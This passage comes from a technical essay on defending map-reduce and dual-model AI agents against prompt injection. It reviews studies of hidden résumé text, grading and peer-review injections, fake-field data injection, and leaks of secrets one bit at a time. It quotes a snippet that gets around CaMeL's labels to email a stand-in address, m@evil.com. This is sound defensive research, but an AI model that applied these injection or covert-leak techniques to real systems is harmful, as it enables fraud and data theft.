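Dongol (2026), in *Relativising Integrity and Robustness*, separates these harms by comparing the real agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan and reads untrusted text but never obeys it. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email, and the invoice contains an order to change the payee to Mallory. Obeying that order gives the attacker nothing new, since a forged invoice could have named Mallory as the payee. Obeying an order to pay Mallory a further £1,000 or to delete Bob's email does give the attacker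 something new, because no invoice would make the reference agent do either. An agent that passes this comparison can still be unsafe, because even the reference agent would pay Mallory if the invoice were forged.

By the same standard, if a file's only effect is that it gets attached, the attacker has achieved nothing that a forged invoice couldn't. Making the model send other suppliers' invoices to an outsider goes beyond what a forged invoice could do. This is possible only if the model reads the file and can choose the recipient.

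When the program attaches the files unread, it should rename them, for example to "invoice-1.pdf", because the original names can contain an injection. It should also take the accounting department's address from the company's own settings. The hidden instructions remain in the attachments, however, and if the accountants use an AI assistant to read their mail, that assistant will be the first model with tools to process them.

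## False answers that fit the type

With isolation and typed outputs, a hostile supplier can only choose the values extracted from its own emails, but the program will act on those values as if they were true. The remaining harm depends on what the program does with them.

### The action attached to the value

A boolean carries at most one bit, but the harm a false one can do depends on how the program uses it. Suppose a map call returns a boolean for whether an email contains an invoice. If the program only files the email, a false "true" puts it in the wrong folder and a clerk moves it. If the program forwards invoices to accounting, the same value means accounting receives a file the attacker chose, sent from a colleague's address. If the program automatically pays invoices under €500, each false "true" can cost the company up to €500.

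| What the value decides | What a false value can do | Who might notice |
|---|---|---|
| Whether a person sees a message | Hide a price increase or a complaint | Nobody, until the consequences appear |
| An item's place in a ranking | Put a product or job applicant ahead of better ones | Few people, since rejected items rarely get a second look |
| Whether to forward a file | Deliver a malicious file from a trusted address | The recipient, if the file looks odd |
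| Which branch of a plan runs | Trigger a step that the planner wrote for other circumstances | Someone who reads the log |
| Who receives a payment | Send the money to the attacker | The real supplier, when no payment arrives |

Errors that hide something are often worse than errors that draw attention to it. A false "urgent" wastes a few seconds of the clerk's time, but a false "not urgent" could keep the clerk from ever opening the email. The mailbox program reduces this risk if it uses the field only to sort the clerk's list, never to remove emails from it.

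Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) studied how false answers can determine which branch of a plan is followed by agents that operate a computer through its screen. A planner that never sees the screen writes the whole plan in advance, with branches for different situations. A quarantined vision model then answers questions such as whether a cookie banner is visible and where it is. An attacker can't add a step to the plan, but a fake cookie banner inside an advertisement made the vision model report a real one. The agent then followed the plan's routine step for dismissing cookie banners, which made it click on the advertisement and open the attacker's site.

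Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. Their example works partly because almost every browsing plan handles cookie notices, so the attacker can predict that step. Redirecting a bank transfer would take several coordinated false answers that match one particular plan. A developer can therefore make a high-stakes action depend on several answers, preferably from items with different authors.

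### Whether a forgery would do as well

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues played down the invoice attack because the attacker could have sent an invoice instead. More generally, a false value adds no new danger if an ordinary-looking document would have produced it anyway, provided that forging that document takes the attacker no more effort than the injection and is no more likely to get caught. A fake invoice meets both conditions because it takes minutes to write and the accountants see whatever arrives in either case.

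The argument fails for the hidden price increase. The supplier wants the email to count as proper notice in a later dispute, so the visible text has to announce the increase plainly. Without an injection, the program would probably file that email under "price change". Hidden text lets the supplier send an email that a person would read as a price increase but the program files under "other".

In résumé screening, an applicant who claims a degree they don't have may get the same score as one who hides an instruction to the model. But the recruiter can read the false claim, ask about it at interview and check it with the university. Hidden text takes almost no effort to add, and the recruiter never sees it. Barach (2026) points out in *ResumeShield* that the text only has to be picked up by the program's text extraction and stay invisible on the page.

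Some job applicants already attempt prompt injection. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026) examined 196,682 real résumés from hireEZ, a recruitment software company, in *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening*. About 1% contained hidden text apparently meant to influence automated screening. In one of the two data sets, the share rose from 0.6–0.8% before 2024 to about 1.2% in 2024, then fell to 0.67% in late 2025. The study did not measure how many attempts worked.

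Over 90% of the résumés with hidden text contained lists of skills, invented experience or text copied from job advertisements, but no instructions. Some dated from 2019, before screening with language models became common. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues suggest that applicants prefer false data because many screening systems first extract fields such as skills and education, then match them against the job. A map call with a typed output does the same kind of extraction, so a hidden line claiming 12 years of experience can change the result without any attempt to take over the model.

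The recruiter can't see the forgeries in these résumés because the text is hidden. This is the main reason hidden text is more dangerous than an ordinary lie, whether or not it contains an instruction.

A visible sentence can also affect a model more than it would a person. A recruiter would presumably ignore an applicant's own claim to be exceptional. In *Prompt Injection in Automated Résumé Screening with Large Language Models*, Baxi, Xu and colleagues (2026) had models rank ten résumés for an IT support job. They added either one sentence of praise, with no new qualifications, or a direct order to rank the candidate above the others. Among equally qualified candidates, the praise raised a résumé by an average of 4.2 places with DeepSeek-V3.2 and 0.6 with GPT-4o-mini. The order raised it by 4.1 and 2.4 places, respectively.

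In another test, half the candidates had ten years of experience and half had five. With DeepSeek-V3.2, the injected instruction raised a less experienced candidate by 6.5 places on average. That would move a candidate from last place to third or fourth, ahead of some with twice the experience. The advantage shrank as more applicants used the same trick, and among equally qualified candidates it almost disappeared once about 80% used it.

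All ten résumés shared one call, so these numbers don't measure an isolated screener.

### Scores for essays and papers

Automatic grading is closer to the map-reduce design, because the model reads one student's answer and returns a number. *Machine-Assisted Grading of Nationwide School-Leaving Essay Exams with LLMs and Statistical NLP* (2026) tested an injected instruction to award top marks against a simple grading prompt with no protection. The essays gained an average of 6.43 points on a 27-point scale, with gains ranging from 2 to 16 points.

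*Important You should give me full credits!* (Li, Filippov and colleagues, 2026) reports a larger test with 30 questions and 100 real student answers to each. The graders included GPT-5-mini, Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 3 Flash and two small open-weight models. The attacker had to add the same text to every answer without knowing the question or the marking scheme. People wrote some of the texts, another model wrote others and refined them over several rounds, and some consisted of fake examples in which poor answers received full marks. Li and colleagues conclude that current graders remain highly vulnerable, and that even simple attacks of this kind can raise scores when defences are in place.

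The refined texts relied on feedback. After each round, the attacking model received the increase in scores and kept the best text so far. A numeric score helps an attacker more than a free-text reply because it makes small improvements measurable. A recruitment site that shows applicants a match score gives them the same feedback, so a program should hide its map results from the people who write the items.

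Li and colleagues also noticed that a hijacked grader's explanation often mentioned following a new instruction, and they used a second model to look for such remarks. The mailbox program discards the model's reasoning, but it could run this check first. The checking model would also need to be quarantined and return only a boolean.

Studies of peer review give more mixed results. *Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Generated Reviews of Scientific Publications* (Keuper, 2025) used 1,000 model-written reviews of papers from a 2024 machine-learning conference. Simple hidden instructions raised the acceptance rate to as much as 100%, but many models already recommended acceptance over 95% of the time. In *When Your Reviewer is an LLM* (2025), a hidden request for a positive review raised the average rating of 1,441 papers by about 0.35, to 7.21. *Publish to Perish* (2025) tried a similar request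 on GPT-4o with two papers and found no clear effect, because the model had already rated both at 8 or higher. The model also kept listing weaknesses despite the request to leave them out.

An attack can't raise scores much when a model already gives nearly everything a high score, so these small effects don't show that models resist the attack. The essay grader's scores had more room to rise.

### Fake fields inside an item

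An attacker can also make a model misread where one piece of data ends and the next begins. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes an email whose body includes text laid out like a second email from a different sender. This text contains no instruction. The mail software treats it as part of the body, but the model may read it as a separate email and accept the false sender's name.

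Older injection attacks, such as SQL injection, need exactly the right punctuation because conventional programs parse input by strict rules. Language models are less strict and, in Choi and colleagues' tests, often treated the wrong kind of quotation mark or bracket as a boundary between fields. Altering the attacker's punctuation therefore doesn't reliably stop the attack.

The tests covered six 2025 models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, with 157 cases based on calendars, emails, shared files, comments, paper reviews and web pages. The tasks resembled map calls. Some required a single field, such as who wrote the first comment, and others required a count, such as the number of events. The models returned the attacker's value in 31 to 43% of attacks on JSON data and 33 to 100% of attacks on web pages, where both OpenAI models were at 100%. A complete fake record worked better than a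 few loose fake fields, which succeeded in 12 to 20% of attacks on JSON.

Choi and colleagues tried two defences. Randomisation adds six random characters to each real field name and tells the model to trust only names with that ending. It cut the attack success rate on JSON to 0–3%, with little loss of accuracy for most models. On web pages, random characters replaced the numbers that identify buttons, and this stopped every attack unless the attacker guessed the characters. Sanitisation removes quotation marks, brackets and similar characters from untrusted text. It was about as effective on JSON, but accuracy on harmless data fell from 81–85% to 68–72% because the filter also damaged web addresses and file paths.

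Randomisation worked less well in a complete agent, where 28.7% of attacks still succeeded. Most of the successful attacks added a fake entry to a list that the agent processed as a whole, for example by totalling a history of transactions. The agent included the fake entry even though its field names lacked the right ending.

Map-reduce avoids part of this problem. If one model call read 200 emails and counted the urgent ones, a supplier could raise the count by writing one email that looked like ten. When each email gets its own call and code counts one result per email, the supplier's email counts at most once. But the supplier can still falsify facts about its own email. If the program gives the model the sender and date along with the body and asks for them back, the model may return a false sender or date written in the body.

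Keeping the planner away from untrusted text doesn't prevent these errors either. Choi and colleagues tested CaMeL, the two-model defence, without its rules restricting how data may be used. Attacks using false data succeeded 25% of the time, compared with 49% against the undefended agent. They succeeded against CaMeL because the quarantined model extracted the wrong values and the plan used them.

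### Whether lying to the model is prompt injection

Jacob and colleagues don't count false information as prompt injection. They also argue that a quarantined model can't select actions, so even if an attacker hijacks it, "no harm will be done to the agent overall".

Their own shopping agent, which rates each review's support for a product from 0 to 10, shows the limits of that claim. A review could contain an instruction to return 10 or simply praise the product dishonestly, and only the instruction would count as prompt injection by their definition. In either case, the privileged model receives a 10 and may buy the wrong product.

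In *Beyond Instruction Override*, Zhang, Bertran and colleagues (2026) count planted text as prompt injection if it tries to influence a decision that its source has no right to make, whether or not it contains an instruction. In their example, a user asks an agent to settle a refund for a damaged item and names the shop's order record as the basis for the amount. The record allows $899.99, but the buyer's evidence cites a false policy that would raise the refund to $1,074.99. This is an injection because the amount was supposed to come from the order record. If the user had asked only for the buyer's stated reason, a lie about the damage would be misinformation rather than injection, since the buyer is the proper source for that answer.

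In the mailbox example, a supplier is the proper source for its own new prices but has no right to decide whether the clerk reads about them. This distinction also helps a developer find possible checks, because code can consult another source that has authority over a value. A lie may be impossible to detect when the item's author is the only source.

Zhang, Bertran and colleagues built 90 cases of what they call task tampering, in which the agent carries out the user's task but gets an amount, recipient or message wrong. Each case has several attacks with the same goal, and most misrepresent only one thing. The table gives the average attack success rate across five models, first without a defence and then with DRIFT's isolator, which looks for injected text and removes it before the agent reads it.

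| What the planted text misrepresents | No defence | Detection and removal |
|---|---|---|
| The goal of the task | 15.0% | 2.4% |
| The rule for making the decision | 21.2% | 5.4% |
| The consequences of an action | 13.7% | 2.7% |
| Which actions are available | 19.0% | 3.9% |
| The meaning of a value the agent has seen | 12.4% | 9.5% |
| The current facts | 18.6% | 12.1% |

The detector removed most text meant to change the agent's goal but often missed false facts, which look like ordinary task data. Another defence, Progent, restricts which tools an agent may call and with what values. It lowered the overall attack success rate only from 17.0% to 15.4%, because the manipulated agent usually called the right tool with a wrong value that the rules allowed.

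These agents had an advantage over an isolated map call because they had access to the order record. Zhang, Bertran and colleagues examined two models in detail, and when those models openly resisted an attack, they almost always cited the source the user had named. A map call that reads only the buyer's message has nothing to compare it with, so isolation makes it more important for code to check the answer afterwards.

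### Taking facts from code and records

The most reliable defence against false values is to avoid asking the model for anything the program can get elsewhere. The mail server records when an email arrived and which domain sent it, and the program assigns the email's number. If the model doesn't need these facts for its task, the program can also leave them out of the map call so the model can't confuse them with the body.

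When a system handles payments, the map call can indicate that an email contains an invoice, but the program should take the account number from the supplier's existing record. A supplier that manipulates the call can then trigger a payment only to its own account on record. If an invoice gives a different account, a person should confirm the change by calling a number the company already has, since the number in the email may belong to an attacker.

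Later checks can limit the damage from some false values. If an email announcing a price increase is filed under "other", the program can't detect the error from its records, but it can compare the prices on the next invoice with the agreed ones and stop the payment if they differ. But no record can confirm whether a complaint is urgent or a review is honest.

Strict rules about where values may come from can also block useful work. In the task-tampering tests, CaMeL allowed important values only from trusted fields. This reduced the attack success rate to 1.3%, but it also reduced the share of tasks that agents completed when there was no attack from 95.3% to 13.3%. Such a rule is easier to apply in the mailbox because the developer knows in advance which few values the program needs.

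### Removing what a person can't see

If the program removes hidden text, applicants can still lie, but only where a recruiter can see it. For an email or web page, the program can pass on only the text that would appear on screen. For a PDF, it can turn each page into an image and read the text from that.

Barach tested a screener that removes hidden text, among other defences, on 104 synthetic documents. Every attack that its detector missed was in visible text. This is weak evidence for the defence as a whole because the "model" was a simple program that obeyed only instructions outside a marked block of data, a rule that real models follow less reliably.

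General injection detectors do poorly on real résumés. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues tried three on 10,000 résumés, 1% of which contained hidden text. Two found only 5% and 7% of the attacks. The third found 87%, but fewer than 1% of its warnings were correct.

Their own detectors look for hidden text instead. The first checks font size, colour and the pixels on the page, then asks a model about the suspicious passages. About 86% of its warnings were correct, and it cost $0.0001 per résumé. The second has a vision model compare the page with the extracted text. It was right 93% of the time but took 25 seconds and cost $0.013 per résumé. Checking 200 documents would cost $0.02 with the first detector and $2.68 with the second. The second would therefore cost more than the mailbox's map calls on any of the models priced earlier.

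### Asking a second model or another question

The program could send each email to two different models and refer it to the clerk if their answers differ. An attack that fools each model 30% of the time would fool both 9% of the time if the failures were independent. But both models read the same text, so an attack that works on one may well work on the other, and the rate for fooling both could be close to 30%.

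Foerster and colleagues tested two such checks against their fake cookie notices and a second attack that made tiny changes to an advertisement's pixels. One check compared the vision model's answer with the page's underlying code. It caught the fake notice when the code labelled the banner as an advertisement, but failed on a type of banner that let the attacker replace the label. The other check asked independent models to confirm the answer. It could not reliably tell fake cookie notices from real ones without disrupting normal browsing, and the pixel attack got past it even at a setting that produced many false alarms. It also raised token use from 1.9 to 6.6 times that of the undefended agent.

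These results come from screenshots, and the attackers knew roughly what the plan would be. A second model may do better on short emails. It could still help against an attacker who has prepared for only one model, provided the clerk has time for the extra emails. If the models disagree about 5% of the mailbox even without an attack, the clerk has ten extra emails to handle.

Changing the question may work against crude attacks. *Hidden Prompts in Manuscripts Exploit AI-Assisted Peer Review* (2025), a commentary on hidden instructions in papers, reports that in an informal test the instructions had no effect when the author explicitly asked the model for criticism. For the mailbox, one call could ask whether an email announces a price change and another whether the clerk could safely ignore it. An instruction to answer "false" to everything would then produce conflicting answers. An attacker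 who expects both questions could instead assert that the email contains nothing important, which would make the answers wrong but consistent.

### More resistant models and human review

A model with strong training against injections is worth using in the map call, but the training helps more against injected instructions than against false data. In Choi and colleagues' agent tests, GPT-5.2 without additional defences obeyed 0.2% of 935 injected instructions, but 49.1% of 108 false-data attacks succeeded. The instructions came from an existing benchmark, so the first rate may be higher against an attacker who adapts. Zhang, Bertran and colleagues found a smaller gap, but the choice of model still mattered. Without a defence, their attacks succeeded 11% of the time against Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 23% against DeepSeek V3.1.

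A person can approve actions with serious consequences, such as a first payment to a new account or a rejection based mainly on a score, but the approval's usefulness depends on what that person sees. Choi and colleagues attacked three coding agents, Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, with a comment that falsely appeared to come from a project's maintainer. All three asked the user before running the attacker's command, but they described the command as the maintainer's fix. Choi and colleagues did not test this on users, but they expect many would approve. A reviewer should therefore see the original document and facts from the program's own records, not the model's explanation. For a résumé, showing the extracted years of experience next to the page would reveal a claim made in hidden text.

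Approval doesn't help with hidden emails, because the program never sends them to anyone for approval. The clerk can instead read a random sample of the emails filed under "other". If the sample covers 10% of them, the clerk has a 10% chance of finding a single hidden price increase. A supplier who hides one email every month for a year has a 72% chance of being caught at least once (1 − 0.9¹²).

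## Secrets that leak through permitted answers

A false value compromises integrity by making the program do the wrong thing. A typed value can also break confidentiality by revealing a company secret to an outsider, even when the program acts correctly on every answer. The capacity of a value limits how much information a hijacked call can leak through it.

### Three conditions and a four-digit code

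A typed answer leaks a secret only if the map call's context contains the secret, the item makes the answer depend on it, and someone outside can observe a consequence of the answer. The threat model assumes that any supplier can meet the second condition. The mailbox program so far meets neither of the other two conditions, because each call contains only the task prompt and one email, and the code only moves emails between folders that no supplier can see.

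A convenient feature could change both. Suppose customers also write to the mailbox, and the program answers routine questions with a standard reply. To help the model decide whether a question is routine, the developer has the program look up the customer's record by the customer number in the email and add it to the call. The model returns a boolean, and the program sends the reply if it is true. The record includes a four-digit code that the customer gives over the phone to confirm orders.

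An attacker who knows the customer's number can send an email with hidden text telling the model to return true if the code is 5,000 or higher. Whether a reply arrives reveals which half of the range the code is in. Each further email halves the remaining possibilities, so 14 emails are enough to find any of the 10,000 possible codes (log₂ 10,000 ≈ 13.3). The attacker can also send all 14 at once, using each to get one binary digit of the code. In both cases, every answer fits the schema and none contains the code as text.

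| What the sender can observe | Bits per email | Emails needed to find any code |
|---|---|---|
| Whether a guessed code is correct | About 0.0015 at first | Up to 9,999 |
| Whether a reply arrives | 1 | 14 |
| Which of four standard replies arrives | 2 | 7 |
| A reply the model writes freely | More than 13.3 | 1 |

In the first row, code rather than a model compares a number in the email with the record, so the attacker can learn only whether one guess is right. A hijacked model is far more dangerous because the attacker can choose which question it answers.

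An unreliable model slows this attack down but doesn't stop it. If the model answers each hidden question correctly 90% of the time, 14 emails recover the whole code only 23% of the time. Asking each question five times and taking the majority answer raises this to 89% if the errors are independent, but takes 70 emails. *Bits Leaked per Query* (2025) tested seven models against three kinds of attack, including extraction of the developer's instructions. The number of queries an attacker needed was roughly inversely proportional to the bits leaked per query. Revealing the model's reasoning or its token scores leaked about half a bit more per query. It also cut the median number of queries for a jailbreak from thousands to tens, which is another reason to discard a map call's reasoning.

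The amount that can leak also has an upper limit. *L3M* (2026), which presents an open-source system for running groups of agents, describes how to calculate this limit, although the released software doesn't implement the calculation. The design counts the secret data that enters an agent and the data the agent sends out afterwards. The leak can't exceed the smaller of the two totals, because processing data can't add information about its source. For example, an agent that has read 64 secret bytes and sends two 50-byte messages has leaked at most 64 bytes. A choice among N options counts as log₂ N bits however much the agent read before choosing, provided the options themselves contain nothing derived from the secret. A longer customer record therefore gives the attacker more to ask about, but each email can still leak at most one bit.

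### Direct flows and inferred secrets

Noninterference, the strictest common definition of secrecy, requires that what an outsider observes not depend on the secrets. The reply program violates it, but so do many useful assistants. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of a calendar assistant that answers meeting requests with its owner's free times. The owner wants this disclosure, but noninterference forbids it.

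FIDES guarantees a weaker property called explicit secrecy. Besides labelling data by trust, it can label data with the people allowed to read it. When the system combines two pieces of data, only people allowed to read both may read the result, and a tool may send data only to permitted readers. This prevents a direct flow, such as copying the customer's code into a message to a stranger.

Explicit secrecy requires that, for any given sequence of actions, changing the secrets doesn't change the public effects. It doesn't cover what an observer infers from which tools the agent called. In the reply program, the secret decides between two sequences, one that sends a standard reply and one that doesn't. Neither sequence copies any secret data, so the program satisfies explicit secrecy while leaking one bit per email.

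Costa and colleagues accepted this gap deliberately. They argue that noninterference would essentially stop an agent from calling tools with public effects once it has called any tool that may have read something secret. Their model also leaves out signals such as timing and network packet length.

A system can try to close the gap by labelling decisions as well as data, so that anything the program does because of a secret also counts as secret. Garby and colleagues show how easily this goes wrong in CaMeL, which refuses to send an email from inside a branch that depends on a secret. Their example gets round the rule with two extra variables, roughly as follows:

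```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false and labels it secret. It then skips the change to `rich`, which stays true and keeps its public label, so the last line sends the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. CaMeL labels only the variables that change in the branch that runs, so it doesn't label `rich` secret even though the balance determines whether `rich` changes.

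LLMbda prevents a similar leak by stopping the program when a branch that depends on a secret tries to write to a public conversation. An observer may still learn something from whether the program stopped. Garby and colleagues prove a version of noninterference that permits this remaining leak, as most such guarantees do. The leak becomes serious if an attacker can trigger the stop repeatedly, as with CaMeL's retry loop.

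### Proofs about agents with two models

Dongol studied 25 small agents in Isabelle/HOL, software that checks mathematical proofs. The test again compares each agent with a reference agent that never obeys untrusted text. An agent fails if an injection lets the attacker distinguish two secrets that the attacker could not distinguish in the reference agent with any input.

Three of the examples use the dual-model design. A fixed plan reads the user's private notes and an email from the attacker, then gives both to a quarantined model. In the simplest version, the plan sends the model's answer to the attacker as a reply. An injection in the email makes the model quote the notes in its answer, so the attacker receives them even though the model has no tools.

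The second version adds labels like CaMeL's, which mark any answer computed from the notes as private. A monitor, which is code that allows or refuses each tool call, refuses any call that would send a private value to the attacker. Dongol proves that this version is secure no matter how the quarantined model behaves. But the model also reads the notes when it writes an honest reply, so every reply is labelled private and the monitor refuses it.

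In the third version, the plan uses the answer to decide whether to send the attacker a 1 or a 0. Both numbers are public constants written into the plan, so they pass the monitor's check. An injection can make the model's answer depend on the notes, so the attacker learns one bit about them from the number. This agent still satisfies explicit secrecy. CaMeL has a strict mode that also labels values with the conditions that controlled them, which should prevent this leak, but Dongol did not model it.

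The reply program leaks in almost the same way, except that the signal is a reply or silence instead of a 1 or 0. A proof could miss the difference between a reply and silence, though. Dongol's basic observer sees the content and order of messages, but the definition compares only runs in which the same number of messages reach the attacker between reads. A second observer, who also sees when each step happens, detects one leak of this kind, in which the agent is allowed to fetch only a newsletter's address. An injection tells the agent to fetch the newsletter if the secret is 0 and the attacker's own address otherwise. The monitor blocks the second request, so the attacker learns whether the secret is 0 by seeing whether a fetch happened.

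Passing the main test doesn't limit how much an injection leaks, either. Suppose the honest program tells a sender whether a guessed code is correct. An injection that sends the whole code would pass, because for any two codes there is some guess that distinguishes them. By the table above, the sender would then need one email to learn the code instead of up to 9,999. The injection fails Dongol's stricter definition, in which the reference agent's input can't depend on the secret.

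### Refusals, errors and timing

Blocking a message can also reveal what was in it. If Dongol's attacker can see the second agent's refused replies, including their arguments, the attacker can read whatever the model wrote about the notes. Showing only the name of the refused tool is harmless in that case, because the monitor refuses the same tool whatever the notes contain. In another example, a private setting determines whether the agent may use an internal tool. An injection makes the agent try the tool, and a refusal showing only the tool's name is enough to reveal the setting.

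A model's refusals can leak secrets in the same way. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes an attack in which the attacker asks an agent to clean up a mixture of real and invented records. The agent refuses to delete the real records, which reveals which ones they are.

Timing can reveal a secret even when the message doesn't change. One of Dongol's agents sends a reply only after the user has approved its exact text. An injection tries to make the agent send a piece of private data instead, and the monitor allows this only if the data matches the approved text. The attacker receives the same message either way, but it arrives one step earlier if the data matches.

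*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) lists loop counts, errors and timing as side channels in CaMeL. The paper gives no measurements, so its list is useful as a checklist. A map-reduce program that runs a fixed sequence of steps and reads each email once avoids only part of the problem.

| Signal | How it can reveal a secret | In the mailbox program |
|---|---|---|
| Loop count | The program contacts a server as many times as a secret number | The emails determine the number of first attempts, but a hijacked call can cause retries |
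| Error | The program fails only if the secret meets some condition | A hijacked call can fail on purpose, which the sender notices if a failure brings an error notice or a clerk's reply |
| Timing | The program takes longer for some secrets | A hijacked call can reason at length before giving the same answer, which delays an immediate reply |

These signals leak information in addition to the boolean. If the sender can distinguish a fast reply, a slow reply and silence, each email leaks about 1.6 bits, and nine emails are enough to find the code.

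### Removing the secret or the signal

The most reliable protection is still to keep any secret the task doesn't need, such as the phone code here, out of the map call. If the model can classify the question from the email alone, the program can consult the customer's record afterwards. The result may still reveal something, because if the program replies only to customers who have paid their bills, for example, a reply shows that this customer has paid. But the attacker can't change that rule to make the reply depend on the phone code.

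Some tasks need private text, such as deciding whether a complaint matches the company's notes on earlier calls. The program should then select the record by the authenticated sender, not by a number in the email. This keeps strangers from reading a customer's record through the model, but the customer could still extract notes the company wanted to keep from them.

The program can also make its visible behaviour uniform, for example by acknowledging every email with the same text as soon as it arrives, before any model reads it. Dongol proves that a similar order works for an agent that may send only one message. The agent sends it before reading the attacker's email, so an injection can't make it send another. But such a reply can't answer the customer's question, and a clerk's later response may still depend on the model's answer.

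Sending all replies at a fixed hour hides how long each call took, as long as every call has finished by then. It doesn't hide which emails received a reply, so 14 emails still reveal 14 bits. Tallam and Miller recommend grouping outgoing requests to hide timing. They also recommend limiting loops, using a single result format for success and failure, and padding every run to the longest possible time. To save money, they suggest putting many items into one prompt, which would undo the isolation between emails. The mailbox program can group its replies safely as long as it keeps the model calls separate.

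Labels that cover decisions as well as data would block every reply from the program, because each one depends on a call that read the private record. FIDES can make an exception for untrusted booleans, and it can do the same for secret ones, which is called declassification. Here, that exception would let the code leak one bit at a time.

A company that accepts a small leak per answer therefore needs to limit the total. *Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) tests a leakage budget for a small local model that reads private documents and works with a model in the cloud. Across 48 questions designed to extract a planted code, the system revealed it 46 times without a budget and never with a budget of 4 nats (about 6 bits). The budget limits how much an answer can disclose compared with a public reference, but doesn't measure what any one answer reveals. With one of the two methods tested, the median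 answer used about 14 bits, equivalent to 14 booleans.

The simplest budget for the mailbox is a limit on automatic replies. The program should count them for each customer record as well as for each sender, since an attacker with several email accounts can ask about the same record from all of them. It must also count emails that received no reply, because the lack of a reply also reveals information. With a limit of one email a day, the attacker needs two weeks to learn the code. If the company changes the code every week, the attacker learns at most 7 bits about each one, which leaves about 78 possibilities. This kind of limit does little to protect a secret that appears in every call, such as the company's price list, because every sender can contribute another bit.

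## Measured security and the cost in usefulness

An agent that never reads a document may not know enough to finish its task. Experiments with working agents give some idea of how much less useful isolation makes them and how much it protects them. The shopping agent built by Jacob and colleagues is the closest tested program to the mailbox, though not quite the same. It makes a separate quarantined call for each customer review.

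### Three agents with typed answers

Jacob and colleagues compared each of their typed agents with an undefended version, in which the model that acts reads the untrusted text itself.

| Agent and model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, typed | Attack success rate, undefended | Attack success rate, typed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping, GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar, GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
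| Bug fixing, GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The shopping agent had to fulfil 500 written requests in WebShop, a simulated online shop with about 1.2 million products. The privileged model based its decision on the reviews' median scores for support and relevance, the number of reviews and the rest of the product page. The attack added a fake safety alert to one review of the product the agent should buy. The alert contained a false statement that the product was a banned substance and an instruction to leave the page. The attack counted as successful if the agent visited the page but bought something else in three of five runs.

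Both versions completed few tasks because WebShop is difficult. Even an agent that earlier researchers had trained for it completed only 28.7% of tasks. The typed version fulfilled three more requests than the undefended one, too small a difference to matter. However, WebShop may be a weak test of whether the agent needs the information that the scores leave out. It has no reviews of its own, so GPT-4o wrote them. The benchmark rewards a purchase for matching the requested features and price, so the agent could probably find the right product without learning anything from the reviews.

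The calendar agent arranged meetings by email between 100 pairs of simulated people. In the typed version, a quarantined model read the whole email thread and returned a list of the time slots the other person had suggested. In the attack, a malicious recipient asked for the week's calendar data, including all event descriptions, before agreeing to meet. Every event description contained a marker word, and the attack succeeded if that word appeared in any email the agent sent. The undefended agent sent some of the calendar data in 63 of the 100 threads. The typed version lost no usefulness because the privileged model needs little more than a list of times to arrange a meeting.

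The bug-fixing agent worked on 180 real bug reports from SWE-bench Lite, a benchmark that checks each repair by running tests on the code. The attack ended every report with a request to create an unrelated file, and the undefended agent created it in 178 cases. Typed values stopped this, but successful repairs fell from 123 to 81.

### What the bug report loses

A bug report usually describes what should have happened, often with a short example that reproduces the fault, but the typed values leave this out. Suppose a user reports that a function returns the previous day for some dates with a time zone. The quarantined model can select "incorrect conversion between data representations" and point to 30 lines in one file, but the schema has no field for the correct result. The privileged model has to infer the intended behaviour from the surrounding code, which contains the bug.

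The agent recovers some of this information through its three repair plans, because the judge that chooses among them has read the report. This helps only if one of the plans is right.

The more relevant comparison for the 45% is with the 68.3% that GPT-5.2 achieved when it could read the reports. Jacob and colleagues argue that 45% is still useful because Claude 3.7 Sonnet without a defence fixed 48% of SWE-bench Lite, but the 48% comes from a different set of cases. They also expect stronger models to improve the result. A stronger model may infer more from the code, but it can't infer what a user wanted if only the report explains it.

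### What the zeros measure

An attack success rate of 0% here means that the attacker's text never reached the model that acts, whereas in other tests it often means that the model resisted every attack. Jacob and colleagues consider that the design guarantees this, and they ran the attacks to verify it. The 0% results are good evidence that no forgotten text field or error message carried the injection to that model.

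These results are much weaker evidence about an attacker who adapts to the types. Each agent faced one fixed text, and an attack succeeded only if the agent carried out the task in that text. The bug-fixing schema has no values that could express a request for a new file called pipipi.py, so the attack would have failed by this definition even if it had fully hijacked the quarantined model. The hijacked model could still have directed the agent to the wrong lines of code, but that would have counted as a failed attack. Jacob and colleagues, who don't count misleading inputs as prompt injection, acknowledge that such inputs could make the agent less useful.

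The shopping test comes closer to measuring the effect of false values because it counts any purchase the attacker diverts. But the attacker controlled only one review per product, and one false score usually has little effect on a median. The privileged model also reads the product description directly, and Jacob and colleagues treat only the reviews as untrusted. In many real shops, an outside seller writes the description and could put an injection in it.

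In the bug-fixing test, the quarantined model can run shell commands on a copy of the code to find the fault. It does this inside a container, which separates it from the rest of the computer, and the privileged model then starts with a clean copy. The test examines only the final patch, so it would also miss a hijacked model that sent the code to an outsider from inside the container. A company using this design would have to block the container's network access as well as restrict the output types.

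### FIDES on 97 tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the chat service Slack. The attacks are designed to make the agent do something other than the user's task, such as invite a stranger to the Slack workspace. Costa and colleagues used a fixed attack whose author knows which tools the agent has.

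Without policies, 152 injections succeeded against a basic GPT-4o agent. FIDES hides untrusted data in variables unless the planner asks to see it, and this alone reduced the number to 21. With the policies switched on, no injection that violated them succeeded against either agent, so that result comes from the policies rather than from hiding the data. Hiding the data lets the planner complete more tasks without violating the policies.

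Costa and colleagues checked the successful attacks by hand and excluded those they considered harmless or wrongly scored. Some exclusions are clearly justified, such as tool calls that the benchmark counted even though the policy had blocked them. Others are more debatable. In one excluded attack, the agent tells the user that a particular place is well worth visiting. This doesn't change the agent's actions or reveal private data, but the user still receives the attacker's advice.

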